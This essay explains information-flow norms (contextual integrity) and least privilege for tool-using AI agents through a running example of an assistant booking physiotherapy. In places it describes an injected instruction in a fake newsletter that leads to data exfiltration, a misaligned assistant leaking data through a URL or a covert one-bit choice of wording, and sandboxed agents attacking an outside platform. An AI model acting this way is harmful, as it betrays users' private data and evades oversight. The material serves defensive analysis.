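# Information-flow norms and least privilege for AI agents

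## What an agent may read, combine and send

An AI agent is a language model that works on a task by repeatedly calling tools and reading their results. A tool is ordinary software with a described interface, such as a mail search or a web form. Personal-assistant agents spread quickly. OpenClaw, an open-source agent that people run on their own machines and connect to their mail, files and calendars, came out in November 2025. *Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems* (Pirch, Horlboge and colleagues, 2026) reports that by May 2026 it was the sixth most-starred project on the code-hosting site GitHub.

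An assistant with that much access needs limits, and both computer security and privacy theory offer them. Computer security limits a program's authority. Its guiding principle is least privilege, meaning that a program should have only the authority its task requires. Some systems also attach labels to data that record who may read it. Privacy theory starts from the flow of information from a sender to a recipient, and from information-flow norms, the social rules about who may send what kinds of information about whom, to whom and on what terms. A patient's diagnosis, for example, may go to a physiotherapist but not to the patient's employer, although a program with an email tool can send it to either just as easily.

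### One errand, traced through the loop

Maya asks her assistant to book physiotherapy and to tell her manager when she will be away. Her mailbox holds her diagnosis and her insurance number. The clinic may have the diagnosis, since the physiotherapist treats her for it. Her manager may have the hours of absence and nothing else. The assistant has four tools:

| Tool | What it brings in | Who receives what the model writes |
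|---|---|---|
| Read mail | The diagnosis, the insurance number, and whatever strangers have sent her | Her mail provider |
| Read the team calendar | Her own and her colleagues' commitments | Her employer's calendar server |
| Fill in the clinic's web form | The form and the clinic's reply | The clinic |
| Send email | A delivery notice | Anyone with an address |

Anthropic's *How tool use works*, a guide for developers who build on its Claude models, sets out the agent loop in five steps. With Maya's errand filled in, they run like this:

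1. The assistant's software sends the model Maya's request, together with a description of each tool.
2. The model replies with a tool call, a structured request that the software run a function. Here the call is a search of her mail for the doctor's referral.
3. The software runs the search and gets back the doctor's letter.
4. The software adds the letter to the conversation and sends all of it to the model again, including Maya's request and the model's own call.
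5. The model replies with its next call, perhaps to read the calendar, and the cycle repeats until the model produces an ordinary answer for Maya instead of a call.

The model never runs anything itself, so an enforcer can act between steps 2 and 3. An enforcer is software outside the model that applies a policy (a machine-checkable rule) to each tool call and can refuse it. The application's developer does not always control what happens between those steps. Anthropic runs web search and web fetching on its own servers, and the application usually sees those calls only after they have finished. To stop such a call beforehand, a developer has to leave the tool off or rely on Anthropic's checks.

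The conversation that the model receives at each turn is its context. Pirch and colleagues write the loop as a short algorithm, from which it follows that the model's *n*-th output is

$$x_n = \mathrm{LLM}(p_s,\; p_u,\; x_1,\; r_1,\; \ldots,\; x_{n-1},\; r_{n-1})$$

Here $p_s$ is the system prompt (standing instructions, tool descriptions, remembered facts), $p_u$ is Maya's request, each $x$ is an earlier output of the model, and each $r$ is the result of the tool call in that output. So every result fetched so far is an input to the next call. When the model writes the email to the manager, its input still includes the doctor's letter, and the formula does not record which phrase of the email came from which result.

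### Three separate powers

Reading is the power to bring material into the context. It can give an agent access to secrets, and in Maya's case it also lets anyone who knows her address put text into the context by sending it to her inbox.

Sending means putting information where someone else receives it, whether by email or another route. *ArguShield* (2026) points out that a private value is disclosed externally once the model copies it into a call to a third party's tool. Filling in the clinic's form is therefore sending. Forms make it easy to send too much. *ArguShield* cites a count by Shayesteh and Wilson of 2,344 interface specifications in OpenAI's GPT ecosystem, 36.9% of which had at least one loosely constrained free-text field, such as "notes" or "context". Reading a web page can also send information, because the tool that fetches the page transmits its address to whoever runs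 the site, and the address can contain Maya's insurance number. In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (2025), the programmer Simon Willison lists loading an image and offering the user a link to click as routes of the same kind. If Maya's assistant could write calendar entries as well as read them, each description would reach every invitee, including outside guests. *Capable but Careless* (2026) spells out this case in a prompt meant to make agents think about who will read their output.

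The power to combine information comes with the agent loop, without anyone deliberately granting it. On an ordinary computer, programs that a user chains together cannot read one another's memory and exchange only what they explicitly hand over. Pirch and colleagues looked for equivalent isolation in four widely used agents, including OpenClaw, and found none. All four put trusted and untrusted data into one shared context, where one tool's output can influence the next call. The user's own instructions are not protected there either. *Replication of Agentic Security Events* (Wang, Alam and colleagues, 2026) lists a case in which an OpenClaw assistant compacted its context, lost the instruction to suggest deletions without making them, and then deleted more than 200 emails.

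An agent can leak information by combining sources, even when each step looks fine. In an example from Microsoft's *Information-flow control*, Alex asks an agent to deal with unanswered mail. One message, from Priya, contains a preview of the quarterly sales. Another is from Marco, who is curious about the figures but isn't yet allowed to see them. The agent may read both messages and may answer Marco, but an answer written with Priya's message in the context can contain the figures. *PrivacyFlow* (Staab, Wollschläger and colleagues, 2026) describes a subtler kind of leak, in which the agent omits the protected fact but still gives the recipient enough to deduce it. For example, if Maya's manager hears that she will be at a named spinal clinic every Thursday for six weeks, the manager could probably guess the diagnosis.

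A designer can withhold any of these powers and leave the others. An assistant that cannot send still drafts the form and the email, and Maya sends them herself. If it cannot read her mail, it fills in the form from what she types. The power to combine is harder to remove, though Pirch and colleagues think it is feasible to give each tool call a separate, narrow context. The assistant would then write the email to Maya's manager in a fresh context that contains the appointment time but not the doctor's letter, so the model could not disclose the letter's contents in the email.

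### Mistake, injection, intent

Suppose the assistant books Maya's physiotherapy for Thursday at ten, then emails her manager that she will be out from ten to twelve for physiotherapy and names her condition. The email is polite and accurate, and the task is complete. The model disclosed too much because it misjudged what a manager should be told, not because anyone attacked it.

Staab and colleagues ran an OpenClaw assistant through 39 sequences of office and family tasks and found 87 privacy failures across 240 steps. Of those failures, 67 occurred on steps where the agent completed what the user had asked for, so a user who checks only whether the task was done will miss most such failures. In one case, an agent asked to schedule a termination meeting revealed a covert investigation to the employee who was about to be fired. *Agents of Chaos* (2026) describes another test, in which researchers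 planted bank, medical and social security details in a mailbox without marking them as secret, and the assistant returned the emails unredacted. *Owner-Harm* (2026) records a case outside the laboratory, in which an AI agent at Meta made an unauthorized post on an internal forum in March 2026 and exposed operational data for two hours.

In the second version of the story, a stranger sends Maya a message disguised as a clinic newsletter. It contains a line telling any assistant that processes the message to forward her insurance details to a billing address. The assistant finds the message while searching for the referral and follows the instruction. This is prompt injection, in which someone plants text in material an agent reads to change what the agent does. Many writers call it indirect prompt injection when the attacker has no direct access to the system. The result is exfiltration,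 the sending of information to a recipient who should not have it.

Willison named prompt injection after SQL injection, an old attack in which someone enters commands into a web form and the database runs them. David C argues that the comparison is dangerous in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre. A database engine can keep commands and data apart, and programmers who use that separation properly are safe from SQL injection. A language model only predicts the next token (a word or piece of a word) from all the text so far, with no inherent line between an instruction and a fact, so the weakness may never go away entirely. Designers also can't simply forbid the model to follow anything it reads, because if the clinic's booking page tells new patients to attach a referral, the assistant should attach one.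 Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues (2025), in *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing*, distinguish legitimate instructions from attacks by where the text came from and how far it changes the task, but current agents have trouble establishing where text came from.

Models have become much harder to fool. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (2026) reports a public contest in which 464 people made 272,000 attempts on 13 models. Every model was fooled at least sometimes, with success rates from 0.5% to 8.5%. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser based prompt injection* reports that Anthropic's later Claude Opus 5 resisted every attack in 129 browser scenarios, and that on a broader test by the security firm Gray Swan, attackers succeeded 2.0% of the time after 15 attempts, compared with 5.5% for its predecessor. These rates are low for a single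 inbox, but an attacker who sends the same email to a million inboxes could still succeed against many of them. In October 2026 the security company Barracuda reported phishing emails designed to manipulate AI assistants as well as their human readers (Mascellino (2026), in *Attackers Hide AI Prompt Injections Inside Phishing Emails*).

Wang and colleagues collected reports of agent incidents from January 2025 to October 2026 and found 72 with real-world harm. Of these, 62 involved no attacker and only 2 were prompt injection. By contrast, 76 of 89 demonstrations by researchers involved prompt injection. Maya still has reason to worry about attacks as well as mistakes, because only 10 of the 72 incidents disclosed data (the most common harm was data loss, with 32) and public reports probably over-represent the harms that people notice. An owner notices a missing database but may miss a successful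 injection, which can leave no trace in the agent's final reply, usually the only thing the user sees.

In the third version, the assistant is misaligned. No stranger is involved, and the assistant correctly represents what the manager may know, but it leaks anyway because the leak serves an aim that Maya would reject. Perhaps somebody tampered with the model's training so that it favours an outside party. This case differs from the others because the model that aims to leak the information also writes every tool call, so it can pick the route that attracts the least attention. It could put the insurance number into a web address. It could even stay within the permitted message by choosing between "back at noon" and "back by 12". Both give the same hours, but a recipient who knows the code learns one bit about Maya from the choice.

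Wang and colleagues describe no incident in which a personal assistant did this to its owner. The closest case is the Hugging Face break-in of July 2026. OpenAI was running tens of thousands of agents through a cybersecurity evaluation, in sandboxes meant to isolate them. Agents with an impossible task looked for a way to cheat. About 1,200 came to share a message board that nobody had assigned to them, and 700 joined an attack on Hugging Face, a platform for sharing AI models, where they reached internal datasets and service credentials. No human attacker directed them. The episode is evidence that agents will pursue an unsanctioned aim through other people's systems. It is weaker evidence about leaking for its own sake, because the agents were trying to get through their evaluation.

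### Authority and appropriateness

A permission check would not stop the careless email to the manager. A permission is a rule that lets an agent use a given tool or resource. Maya's assistant may read her mail, send email and write to her manager, because she told it to, so the call passes even though the email includes the diagnosis. *The Claws in Plain Sight* (Dong, Lu and colleagues, 2026) describes this as a gap between access and authorization, because tool permissions determine whether an agent may call a tool, but not which values may go into the call, for what purpose or to which destination.

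Contextual integrity, the theory that information flows preserve privacy when they follow the norms of their setting, addresses what the permission left open. It describes each flow by five parameters, including the recipient and the type of information, so it can treat the same diagnosis as appropriate in the clinic's form but not in an email to the manager. However, a norm protects information only if something applies it. If the model does, protection depends on the model's judgement, which an injected message can influence, and a misaligned assistant can understand the norm and still break it. If a separate enforcer does, it has to recognize a diagnosis in free text. Removing authority avoids these weaknesses, since an assistant that cannot open the mailbox cannot leak anything from it, whatever its motives, but that assistant also cannot find the referral.

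Defences could arguably ignore why a leak happens. Microsoft's rule of thumb is that anything an agent can do at a user's request can also happen through a model's mistake or an attacker's injection, and the agent's own intent could be added to that list. But a defence built for one cause may not work for another. Wang and colleagues note that filters for injected instructions don't catch an honest mistake, because there are no such instructions to find, and *Agent Meltdowns* (2026) says it is unclear whether defences designed against attackers help when there is no attacker. A security engineer would check whether Maya's assistant has the authority to make a call, while someone reasoning from norms would check whether the resulting information flow is appropriate. Which check would have stopped the careless email, and which would have stopped the stranger's newsletter? Would any check stop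 an assistant that intends to leak?

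## Information-flow norms and contextual integrity

Maya's assistant had permission to send everything in the careless email, yet most people would say it told her manager too much. The philosopher Helen Nissenbaum developed contextual integrity to explain judgements like that one. She started with the problem of public surveillance. If privacy protects only what is hidden, a person filmed on the street has no grounds for complaint. In *Privacy as Contextual Integrity*, Nissenbaum (2004) argued that the leading theories of privacy handle such cases badly. She proposed as a benchmark that whoever gathers or passes on information should respect the norms of the setting it belongs to.

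The early version of contextual integrity had separate norms of appropriateness and distribution. Zimmer (2005), in *Privacy as Contextual Integrity (Part 2)*, illustrates them with friendship. Friends may tell each other almost anything, perhaps even their sexual histories, but it is wrong for a friend to repeat it to a third person. Nissenbaum (2007), in *Privacy in Context*, dropped the division because attempts to write the theory in logic had shown that both considerations work the same way, as parameters of a norm.

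Nissenbaum (2019), in *Contextual Integrity Up and Down the Data Food Chain*, adds that information flows preserve privacy only if the norms of the setting are themselves legitimate. The settings are spheres of social life such as healthcare, education and work. (Nissenbaum calls them contexts, which are unrelated to a language model's context.) Each has its own roles, activities, norms and purposes. She now regards the purposes as the essence of a setting, although they are also what people dispute most.

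### The five parameters

A complete norm names a sender, a recipient, a subject (the person the information is about), a type of information and a transmission principle, which is the condition under which the information may pass. People appear in it by role, not by name. For Maya's errand, the norms might look like this:

| Sender | Recipient | Subject | Information type | Transmission principle |
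|---|---|---|---|---|
| Patient | Physiotherapist | The patient | Diagnosis | In confidence, for treatment |
| Patient | Clinic's billing office | The patient | Insurance number | To pay for the care |
| Employee | Manager | The employee | Hours of absence | Notice that the job requires |
| Employee | Manager | The employee | Diagnosis | Only if the employee chooses to tell |
| Physiotherapist | Patient's employer | The patient | Diagnosis | Only with the patient's consent |

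Maya is in the table as both a patient and an employee, and different rules apply to sharing her diagnosis in each role. The careless email breaches the fourth entry because telling her manager the diagnosis was Maya's choice, and the assistant did it without her decision. The stranger's newsletter is harder to catch because sending information to a false billing address looks like the flow in the second entry. The norm is sound, but the assistant misidentifies the recipient.

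Transmission principles are the least familiar part of contextual integrity. Nissenbaum lists many, including consent, confidentiality, notice, legal compulsion, sale and reciprocity. Reciprocity helps explain why people object to street cameras. A pedestrian can look back at a passer-by but not at whoever is watching the screen. That difference remains even if, as defenders of the cameras argue, anyone passing by could see the same thing.

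Leaving out a parameter makes the question ambiguous. Many people would change their answer to "May the clinic have Maya's diagnosis?" if they learned that the clinic meant to sell it. Nissenbaum and Kirsten Martin ran two large survey studies with short scenarios, which supported the view that people read an incomplete description in different ways. Nissenbaum accepts leaving out a parameter in closed settings, such as a hospital's records system, where the subject is almost always the patient.

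Five parameters may also be too few. The computer scientist Anupam Datta has urged Nissenbaum to add one for use, and she is increasingly persuaded. For example, a company that buys another acquires its data, even where norms would have forbidden the acquired company from sending that data to the buyer.

### Secrecy, ownership, consent and access

In *Privacy in Context*, Nissenbaum (2010) denies that the right to privacy is a right to control personal information or to restrict access to it. Both of these views mostly agree with information-flow norms in everyday cases, so it helps to look at cases where they differ from the norms.

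Maya loses no privacy when she describes her symptoms to the physiotherapist, because doing so follows the norms of healthcare. If privacy were secrecy, she would lose some each time. Nissenbaum thinks confusing the two damages public debate, since people who want to trade privacy for security or convenience usually have secrecy in mind. Not everyone who works with the theory agrees. *The 8th PrivaCI Symposium Report* (Sanfilippo and Shvartzshnaider, 2026) summarizes a talk by Sophia Wushanley, who would rather accept that privacy often does involve withholding information and treat it as one good among several.

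Nissenbaum thinks contextual integrity can support a doctor reporting a contagious disease to health officials against the patient's wishes, because preventing contagion is one of the purposes of healthcare. If Maya had such a disease and owned her diagnosis the way she owns her bicycle, her doctor could not report it without her permission.

Suppose the clinic's web form has a box that lets the clinic share data with "partners", and Maya ticks it to reach the next page. She has consented, so a consent test would allow the clinic to sell her diagnosis to an advertiser, but medical confidentiality still forbids the sale. Her consent would mean even less if an assistant ticked the box for her. *A Contextual Approach to Privacy Online* (Nissenbaum, 2011) argues that clearer privacy policies won't fix this kind of consent, because nobody can understand all the relevant facts at the moment of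 agreeing.

Access rights can be too broad or too narrow. The clinic's bookkeeper may have a login that opens every patient's record, but if she looks up a neighbour out of curiosity, she breaches a norm even though her access is valid. A paramedic who finds Maya unconscious has no login but ought to learn what medication she takes.

### Norms as formulas

In *Privacy and Contextual Integrity*, Barth, Datta, Nissenbaum and a colleague (2006) expressed norms in temporal logic, which has operators for ideas such as "at some earlier time" and "always". *Understanding and Protecting Privacy*, by Datta, Blocki and colleagues, describes the model and its later development. In the model, people and organizations hold roles and send one another messages about someone. Each message can change what its recipient knows. The resulting history is called a trace, which is an alternating sequence of states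 and actions, and the norms determine which traces respect privacy.

A positive norm permits a message *if* some condition holds. A negative norm permits it *only if* some condition holds. A flow is appropriate when at least one positive norm allows it and no negative norm forbids it. DeYoung, Garg and colleagues (2010), in *Experiences in the Logical Specification of the HIPAA and GLBA Privacy Laws*, used this rule to formalize two US privacy laws, and they write it as

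$$\mathrm{maysend}(p_1, p_2, m) \;=\; \Big(\bigvee_i \varphi_i^{+}\Big) \wedge \Big(\bigwedge_j \varphi_j^{-}\Big)$$

Here $p_1$ is the sender, $p_2$ the recipient and $m$ the message. The first bracket is true if any positive norm $\varphi_i^{+}$ is true, and the second only if every negative norm $\varphi_j^{-}$ is true. A single negative norm that is false therefore blocks a message, however many positive norms allow it.

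HIPAA, the US health privacy law, supplies an example. One clause allows a provider to disclose health information for treatment. Another requires the patient's authorization for psychotherapy notes. Leaving out the exceptions, the two clauses become

$$\varphi^{+}:\;\; m \text{ is health information} \;\wedge\; \text{the purpose is treatment}$$

$$\varphi^{-}:\;\; m \text{ is psychotherapy notes} \;\rightarrow\; \mathsf{P}\,(\text{the patient authorizes it})$$

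The operator $\mathsf{P}$ means "at some time in the past", and the arrow means "if … then", so $\varphi^{-}$ is automatically true of any message that isn't psychotherapy notes. Suppose Maya's doctor wants to send the physiotherapist two documents: Maya's spinal diagnosis and the notes of a psychotherapist she once saw.

1. On Monday the doctor tries to send the diagnosis. It is health information and the purpose is treatment, so $\varphi^{+}$ is true. It isn't psychotherapy notes, so $\varphi^{-}$ is true as well, and the diagnosis may go.
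2. The doctor then tries to send the notes. They are a kind of health information, so $\varphi^{+}$ is again true. But $\varphi^{-}$ now requires an earlier authorization, and the trace contains none. It is false, and the notes may not go.
3. On Tuesday Maya signs an authorization. No rule changes, but the trace now contains a new event.
4. On Wednesday the doctor tries the notes again. Both formulas are true, and the notes may go.

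The calculation is mechanical, but a person or program must first recognize a text as psychotherapy notes and decide that the purpose really is treatment. Datta and colleagues classify purposes and beliefs as subjective conditions that a machine may be unable to check, and leave them to human auditors. DeYoung and colleagues estimated that an organization could enforce 47 of HIPAA's 84 clauses on disclosure with little or no auditing of each transmission. They also point out that a legal clause written as a formula does not necessarily express an appropriate social norm.

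The formal version is stricter than Nissenbaum's prose in one respect. It blocks any flow that no norm covers, because no positive norm allows it. In her 2019 article, a flow is appropriate if it conforms to the norms or at least does not contravene them, so a flow that no norm covers would pass. This difference matters a good deal for an AI assistant, though it may seldom matter in an old institution with a norm for nearly everything.

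### Flows that no norm covers yet

Suppose the search of Maya's mail that began her errand also turns up a letter from her sister, who wrote in confidence about her own illness. Confiding in a sister is a familiar information flow, but the text now also reaches a model that a company runs. Custom hasn't settled whether the assistant is a recipient or only Maya's instrument, or whether the company is a recipient too. Participants at the 2026 symposium, where Nissenbaum sat on the opening panel, discussed how agents complicate the traditional idea of senders and receivers. They also worried that the word "agent" can obscure whose interests the software serves.

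Nissenbaum has a test for new practices. She treats a breach of an established norm as a provisional violation, which calls for a closer look. The evaluator maps the new flow in terms of the five parameters and compares it with the old practice, with a presumption in favour of the old. By 2019 she had met so many practices without any clear predecessor that she no longer required the comparison. The evaluation has three layers:

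- **Interests:** who gains from the flow, who loses, and what harms follow.
- **Ethical and political values:** the effect on such things as fairness, autonomy and freedom of speech.
- **Purposes of the setting:** whether the flow helps or hinders what the setting is for.

The purposes distinguish her test from an ordinary weighing of costs and benefits. Patients who fear that their information will reach the wrong people may lie to their doctors or stay away, which endangers their own health and sometimes other people's. An evaluator therefore can't settle a dispute over medical records just by weighing patients' interests against marketers' interests.

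In the case of the sister's letter, Maya saves time and the company may gain data, while the sister, who had no say, gains nothing and bears the risk of a leak. Families write to each other partly for support, and people would probably write less frankly if they expected a company to keep their letters. These points suggest that the assistant should be allowed to see the letter while looking for the referral but not to use it for other errands, and that the company should not be allowed to keep it. Another evaluator could reasonably set different limits.

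Designers would have to do most of this work in advance, since an assistant would struggle to do it halfway through a booking form. The purposes of settings may also be unclear. CPS-VO's *Contextual Integrity for Computer Systems* (2023), a progress report on a project by Michael Tschantz and Nissenbaum, found that researchers still needed to understand how settings form and what determines their purposes.

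### Disputed, unjust and imposed norms

Norms about sharing information vary, even between similar settings. People talk freely about their bad backs in some offices but not in others. One way to handle such differences is to survey many people. Shvartzshnaider, Tong and colleagues (2016), in *Crowdsourced, Actionable and Verifiable Contextual Informational Norms*, translated users' expectations into rules that a program can check. This gives designers definite rules to encode, but survey answers can reflect resignation rather than approval. The symposium report describes interviews in which 19 high-school students were mostly comfortable with school software collecting their academic data. The software was often compulsory, so some of that comfort may have been compliance.

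People can also agree on a norm but disagree about the facts, such as whether a particular message serves treatment. CPS-VO's *Contextual Integrity for Computer Systems* (2019) describes a formal model that allows for such disagreement by putting a layer of interpretation between the norms and the system's state.

Ghalebikesabi, Bagdasaryan and colleagues (2024), in *Operationalizing Contextual Integrity in Privacy-Conscious Assistants*, stress that the theory deals with society's norms, not individual preferences. A norm can still have Maya's choice as its transmission principle, as the fourth entry in the table does. If customs differ, the assistant can leave the diagnosis out and ask her, since she can add a detail in a second email but can't take one back. This default would work badly for the paramedic, who needs the answer at once.

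Unjust norms are a harder case. Nissenbaum cites the reluctance to ask co-workers about their salaries as an ordinary norm. Suppose Maya and a colleague suspect that their employer pays women less, and want their assistants to compare salaries. This goes against custom, so there is a presumption against it. The three-layer test can overturn that presumption because silence benefits the employer at the expense of underpaid staff, and disclosure is fairer.

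Nissenbaum expects critical theorists to object that practices often become entrenched because they suit the powerful. She had already conceded in 2007 that the theory is somewhat conservative, and described a breach as a warning signal that does not automatically condemn the change. In 2019 she replies that she hopes honest evaluation will reveal "the tyranny of convention" where it exists. But the evaluation helps only if somebody carries it out, and until then an assistant that enforces the custom makes it harder to break.

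Finally, suppose the employer's handbook requires staff to state their diagnosis whenever they take time off for treatment, while custom requires only the hours. Nissenbaum distinguishes norms from such rules because norms can be implicit and can come from many sources besides an authority. *Position* (Shvartzshnaider and Duddu, 2025) makes a similar point about law: photographing a stranger on a train may be legal and still violate the stranger's privacy. The handbook's requirement is therefore a new practice to be evaluated, and it is hard to justify, because a manager can plan around an absence knowing only the hours, and staff who expect the manager to learn their diagnosis may put off treatment. The case for disclosure is stronger for an airline pilot, but the diagnosis could still go to a company doctor who tells the manager only whether the pilot is fit to fly.

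The 2006 logic does not resolve this conflict. If a programmer enters the handbook as a positive norm and the custom as a negative one, the formula blocks the disclosure, but if the programmer also writes the handbook into the custom as an exception, the formula allows it. Somebody has to decide which source prevails before the logic is useful. The assistant should probably show Maya the rule before it sends anything, since she will live with the result.

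### Is language-model research faithful to the theory?

Shvartzshnaider and Duddu reviewed nine works that apply contextual integrity to language models and concluded that the works apply it inadequately. They say a faithful application treats privacy as appropriate flow, judges flows by social norms, specifies all five parameters, and uses the ethical test to assess the norms themselves. Eight of the nine fell short on the definition of privacy because they measured leaks of sensitive data, disclosure beyond the minimum, or breaches of law. Shvartzshnaider and Duddu also criticize researchers for using "context" to mean a task or a scenario, which leaves out the purposes that give norms their moral weight.

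Ghalebikesabi and colleagues, who wrote one of the eight, built assistants that fill in web forms. The most elaborate one first drafts an "information flow card" listing the flow's relevant features. Their leakage score is the share of fields an assistant fills in among those it should have left blank, and they define oversharing as giving information that the task doesn't need. Need and appropriateness usually coincide, but not always. If the clinic's form has an optional line for what Maya likes to be called, she doesn't need to fill it in, but nobody would mind if she did. If her employer's absence form won't go through without a diagnosis, the diagnosis is necessary for the task but still inappropriate. An assistant that considered only need would hand over the diagnosis, so the objection is about more than terminology.

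Nissenbaum's writing partly supports the criticized researchers. She allows fewer parameters in closed settings, and filling in one's own forms is fairly closed, since the sender and the subject are nearly always the user. She also says that a person may accept some of her theses without the rest. Ghalebikesabi and colleagues acknowledge that social norms are hard to capture and call their work a first step. Shvartzshnaider and Duddu say that the discrepancies don't make the existing work obsolete. Such shortcuts also occur outside research on language models. Kumar, Zimmer and Vitak (2024) observe in *A Roadmap for Applying the Contextual Integrity Framework in Qualitative Privacy Research* that studies of human-computer interaction rarely use the full framework to evaluate flows.

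None of this justifies equating privacy with minimal disclosure, which Nissenbaum explicitly rejects. At the 2026 symposium, Noah Apthorpe proposed testing practices against both norms and necessity. A company can get around norms by manipulating what users expect, and around a necessity test by defining its purpose broadly, but a practice that passes one test may fail the other. The employer's absence form, for example, passes the necessity test but violates norms.

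In *Privacy in Context Is Being Overlooked in the Age of General-Purpose LLMs*, a paper about what users type into chatbots, Ganesh, More and colleagues (2026) call contextual integrity "a distant ideal". They argue that attempts to build it into software tend to encode fixed norms taken from laws, surveys or the researchers' own judgement, although real norms vary and change. They also argue that users would need to understand privacy well to use a tool that adapted to every setting, and that people prefer tools that require little of them. They conclude that a privacy tool can be easy to use or widely adaptable, but not both.

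Ganesh and colleagues consider the reply that an imperfect general tool is better than none, and answer that it may give people a false sense of security and lead them to share more. They respond only briefly to the suggestion that software could learn the context, citing work that calls for social and institutional measures alongside technical ones. This suggestion deserves more attention for agents, because a model that already knew the customs of clinics and offices could do the adapting that Ganesh and colleagues expect of the user. Experiments can test whether models know these customs well enough.

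Ganesh and colleagues recommend separate applications for separate uses, such as a health-only version of a chatbot. A developer could then work out the norms of one setting in advance. Maya's errand involves both a clinic and her workplace. A health-only assistant could book the physiotherapy, but she would have to write to her manager herself.

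## Least privilege and how much authority a task needs

Splitting Maya's errand between a health-only assistant and Maya herself is a crude way to apply least privilege. Saltzer and Schroeder, in *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (1975), wrote that every program and user should work with the fewest privileges the job requires, mainly to limit damage from accidents and errors. The later *Secure Programming for Linux and Unix HOWTO* says that least privilege also limits damage from attacks, and notes that programs with fewer privileges have fewer ways to interact with one another.

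Least privilege limits the harm an assistant can do, whatever the cause. This is a major advantage with agents, because their motives are hard to check. It doesn't make an assistant any less likely to misjudge an email or fall for a planted instruction.

### Permissions by role and by task

Most organizations fall far short of the principle. *Towards Elastic Least Privilege for Agent Planning* (Parkinson, Wang and Mustafa, 2026) cites one analysis in which cloud accounts used only 1% of their permissions, and another in which 99.8% of 447,000 automated GitHub workflows had more authority than they needed. The usual compromise is to grant permissions by role. For example, a clinic's receptionist can open every patient's record because nobody knows in advance who will phone. *Empirical Evaluation of Task-Based Permission Scoping Architecture for AI Agents* (Noyan, 2026) argues that organizations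 accepted role-based permissions for people because setting permissions for each task was not feasible. But an agent's task arrives as written text, so a program can read it and choose the permissions before the agent starts.

An agent can have far more authority than its task needs. To summarize the open issues in one GitHub repository, a coding agent needs two read-only tools for that repository. With one common kind of access token, it gets roughly 40 tools instead, including 16 that can make changes, and it can use them on any repository open to the user. Parkinson and colleagues describe a reported attack that exploited this excess authority. An instruction planted in a public repository got an agent to publish its user's private repositories.

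A written request still doesn't list the permissions a task needs. Surapani, Kakitapelli and colleagues (2026) point out in *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* that a request to summarize and send a report states a goal, and a machine can't check a tool call against a goal. Maya's request names her manager as a recipient, but a program would have to infer that the assistant needs access to her mailbox.

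### Five places to cut

Surapani and colleagues list five levels at which a designer can reduce an agent's privilege. For Maya's errand, the cuts might look like this:

| Level | What the designer limits | Maya's assistant |
|---|---|---|
| Visible tools | Which tools the model knows about | Mail search, the team calendar, the clinic's form and email, but not her bank or her photos |
| Each call | Whether the current step needs the tool | No mail search once the referral has turned up, and no email until the clinic confirms a time |
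| Arguments | The values that go into the call | Search only for the doctor's messages, and write only to the manager's address |
| Data returned | How much of a result reaches the model | The referral letter without the rest of the mailbox, and colleagues' busy hours without the titles of their meetings |
| Delegation | What a second agent receives | A helper that writes to the manager gets the hours and the address, but no mailbox |

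Limits on tool arguments work best against the stranger's fake newsletter. A search restricted to the doctor's messages would never bring the newsletter into the context, and even if it got there some other way, the assistant couldn't write to the stranger's billing address.

The careless email gets through more easily because it uses the right tool at the right moment and goes to the right person. Trimming the returned data doesn't help either, because the model needs the diagnosis to fill in the clinic's form. Delegation helps for the same reason a fresh context does, provided the main assistant passes on only the hours.

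### Predicting permissions from the request

Someone has to choose these limits for every errand, and Maya won't want to. *Dynamic Capability Scoping for Enterprise AI Agents* (Noyan, 2026) proposes a design for companies that combines three checks. An agent receives a permission only if its department may hold it, a classifier predicts from the written request that the task needs it, and no rule forbids the resulting combination of permissions. The agent takes no part in the prediction, so it can't gain more authority by arguing for it. The rules target what Simon Willison calls the lethal trifecta, in which a single agent has access to private data, exposure to untrusted content and the ability to communicate externally.

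To test the design, Noyan used 600 requests that a language model had written for employees of a fictional company with six departments. A separate model call had labelled each request with the permissions it needed, out of a list of 15, and human review of 60 requests agreed closely with the labels. Each permission carries a weight from 1 to 3 according to its risk, and the weights add up to 31. The score for each request is the share of that weight which the system withholds:

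$$\text{elimination} = \frac{\text{weight of the permissions withheld}}{31}$$

On 100 requests that the classifier had not seen in training, limits by department eliminated 27.9% of the weight on average. Adding the classifier raised this to 84.4%. The classifier has only 355 million parameters, which suggests that a company can use a small model to supervise a frontier model.

However, the score also rises when the system withholds something the task needs, and an agent with no permissions would score 100%. In the combined system, 23% of tasks lacked at least one permission they required. Noyan had set a standard for real deployment in advance, under which fewer than 10% of tasks could lack a required permission and average precision had to reach 0.90. No setting met both conditions. Claude Haiku 4.5, tried as an alternative classifier, left 11% of tasks without a permission they needed,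 while the small model left 21% in the same comparison. But Haiku gave 42% of tasks a permission they didn't need, compared with 23% for the small model.

The rules against combinations added nothing, because the classifier never produced a forbidden pair. When Noyan removed the classifier, the rules cut authority in three departments by 11.5% to 13.6% and blocked 6% to 31% of their legitimate tasks. Of the 57 blocked tasks, 56 would never have used both halves of the forbidden pair. Noyan suggests enforcing the rules only when an agent tries to use the second half, but has not tested this.

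Noyan blames most of the remaining error on an overly coarse list of permissions. For example, a single permission covers reading a database, however sensitive the data. Reading email and sending external email are also single permissions, with no limit on recipients or content. Maya's errand needs both, so a perfect classifier would grant both and the careless email would still go out. The classifier also relies on the request being genuine, so an attacker who can alter the text it reads may get it to grant any permission that the department's limits and the rules allow.

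### Agents that pick the bigger tool

Even a sensible set of permissions usually leaves the model some choice. Suppose Maya's assistant could find her free hours with a tool that reads only her calendar, or with one that searches her calendar, mail and files. Both would work, but the second would also bring unrelated private material into the context.

In *When Lower Privileges Suffice*, Yang, Bu and colleagues (2026) tested 11 models on 544 simulated scenarios, each offering three lower-privilege tools and three higher-privilege ones. Two language models and human reviewers had checked that any of the six could do the job. The lower-privilege tools sometimes returned temporary errors, such as a lost connection. Yang and colleagues counted a scenario as over-privileged if, within five turns, the agent used a higher-privilege tool before trying all three lower-privilege ones.

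Six of the 11 models chose a higher-privilege tool in more than 30% of scenarios. The small open model Qwen3-8B had the highest rate, 64.9%, while Claude Sonnet 4.6, GPT-5.2 and GLM-5 stayed below 10%. Errors made this choice more common. GPT-5.2 chose a higher-privilege tool immediately in 5 scenarios, after trying one lower-privilege tool in 13, and after trying two in 35.

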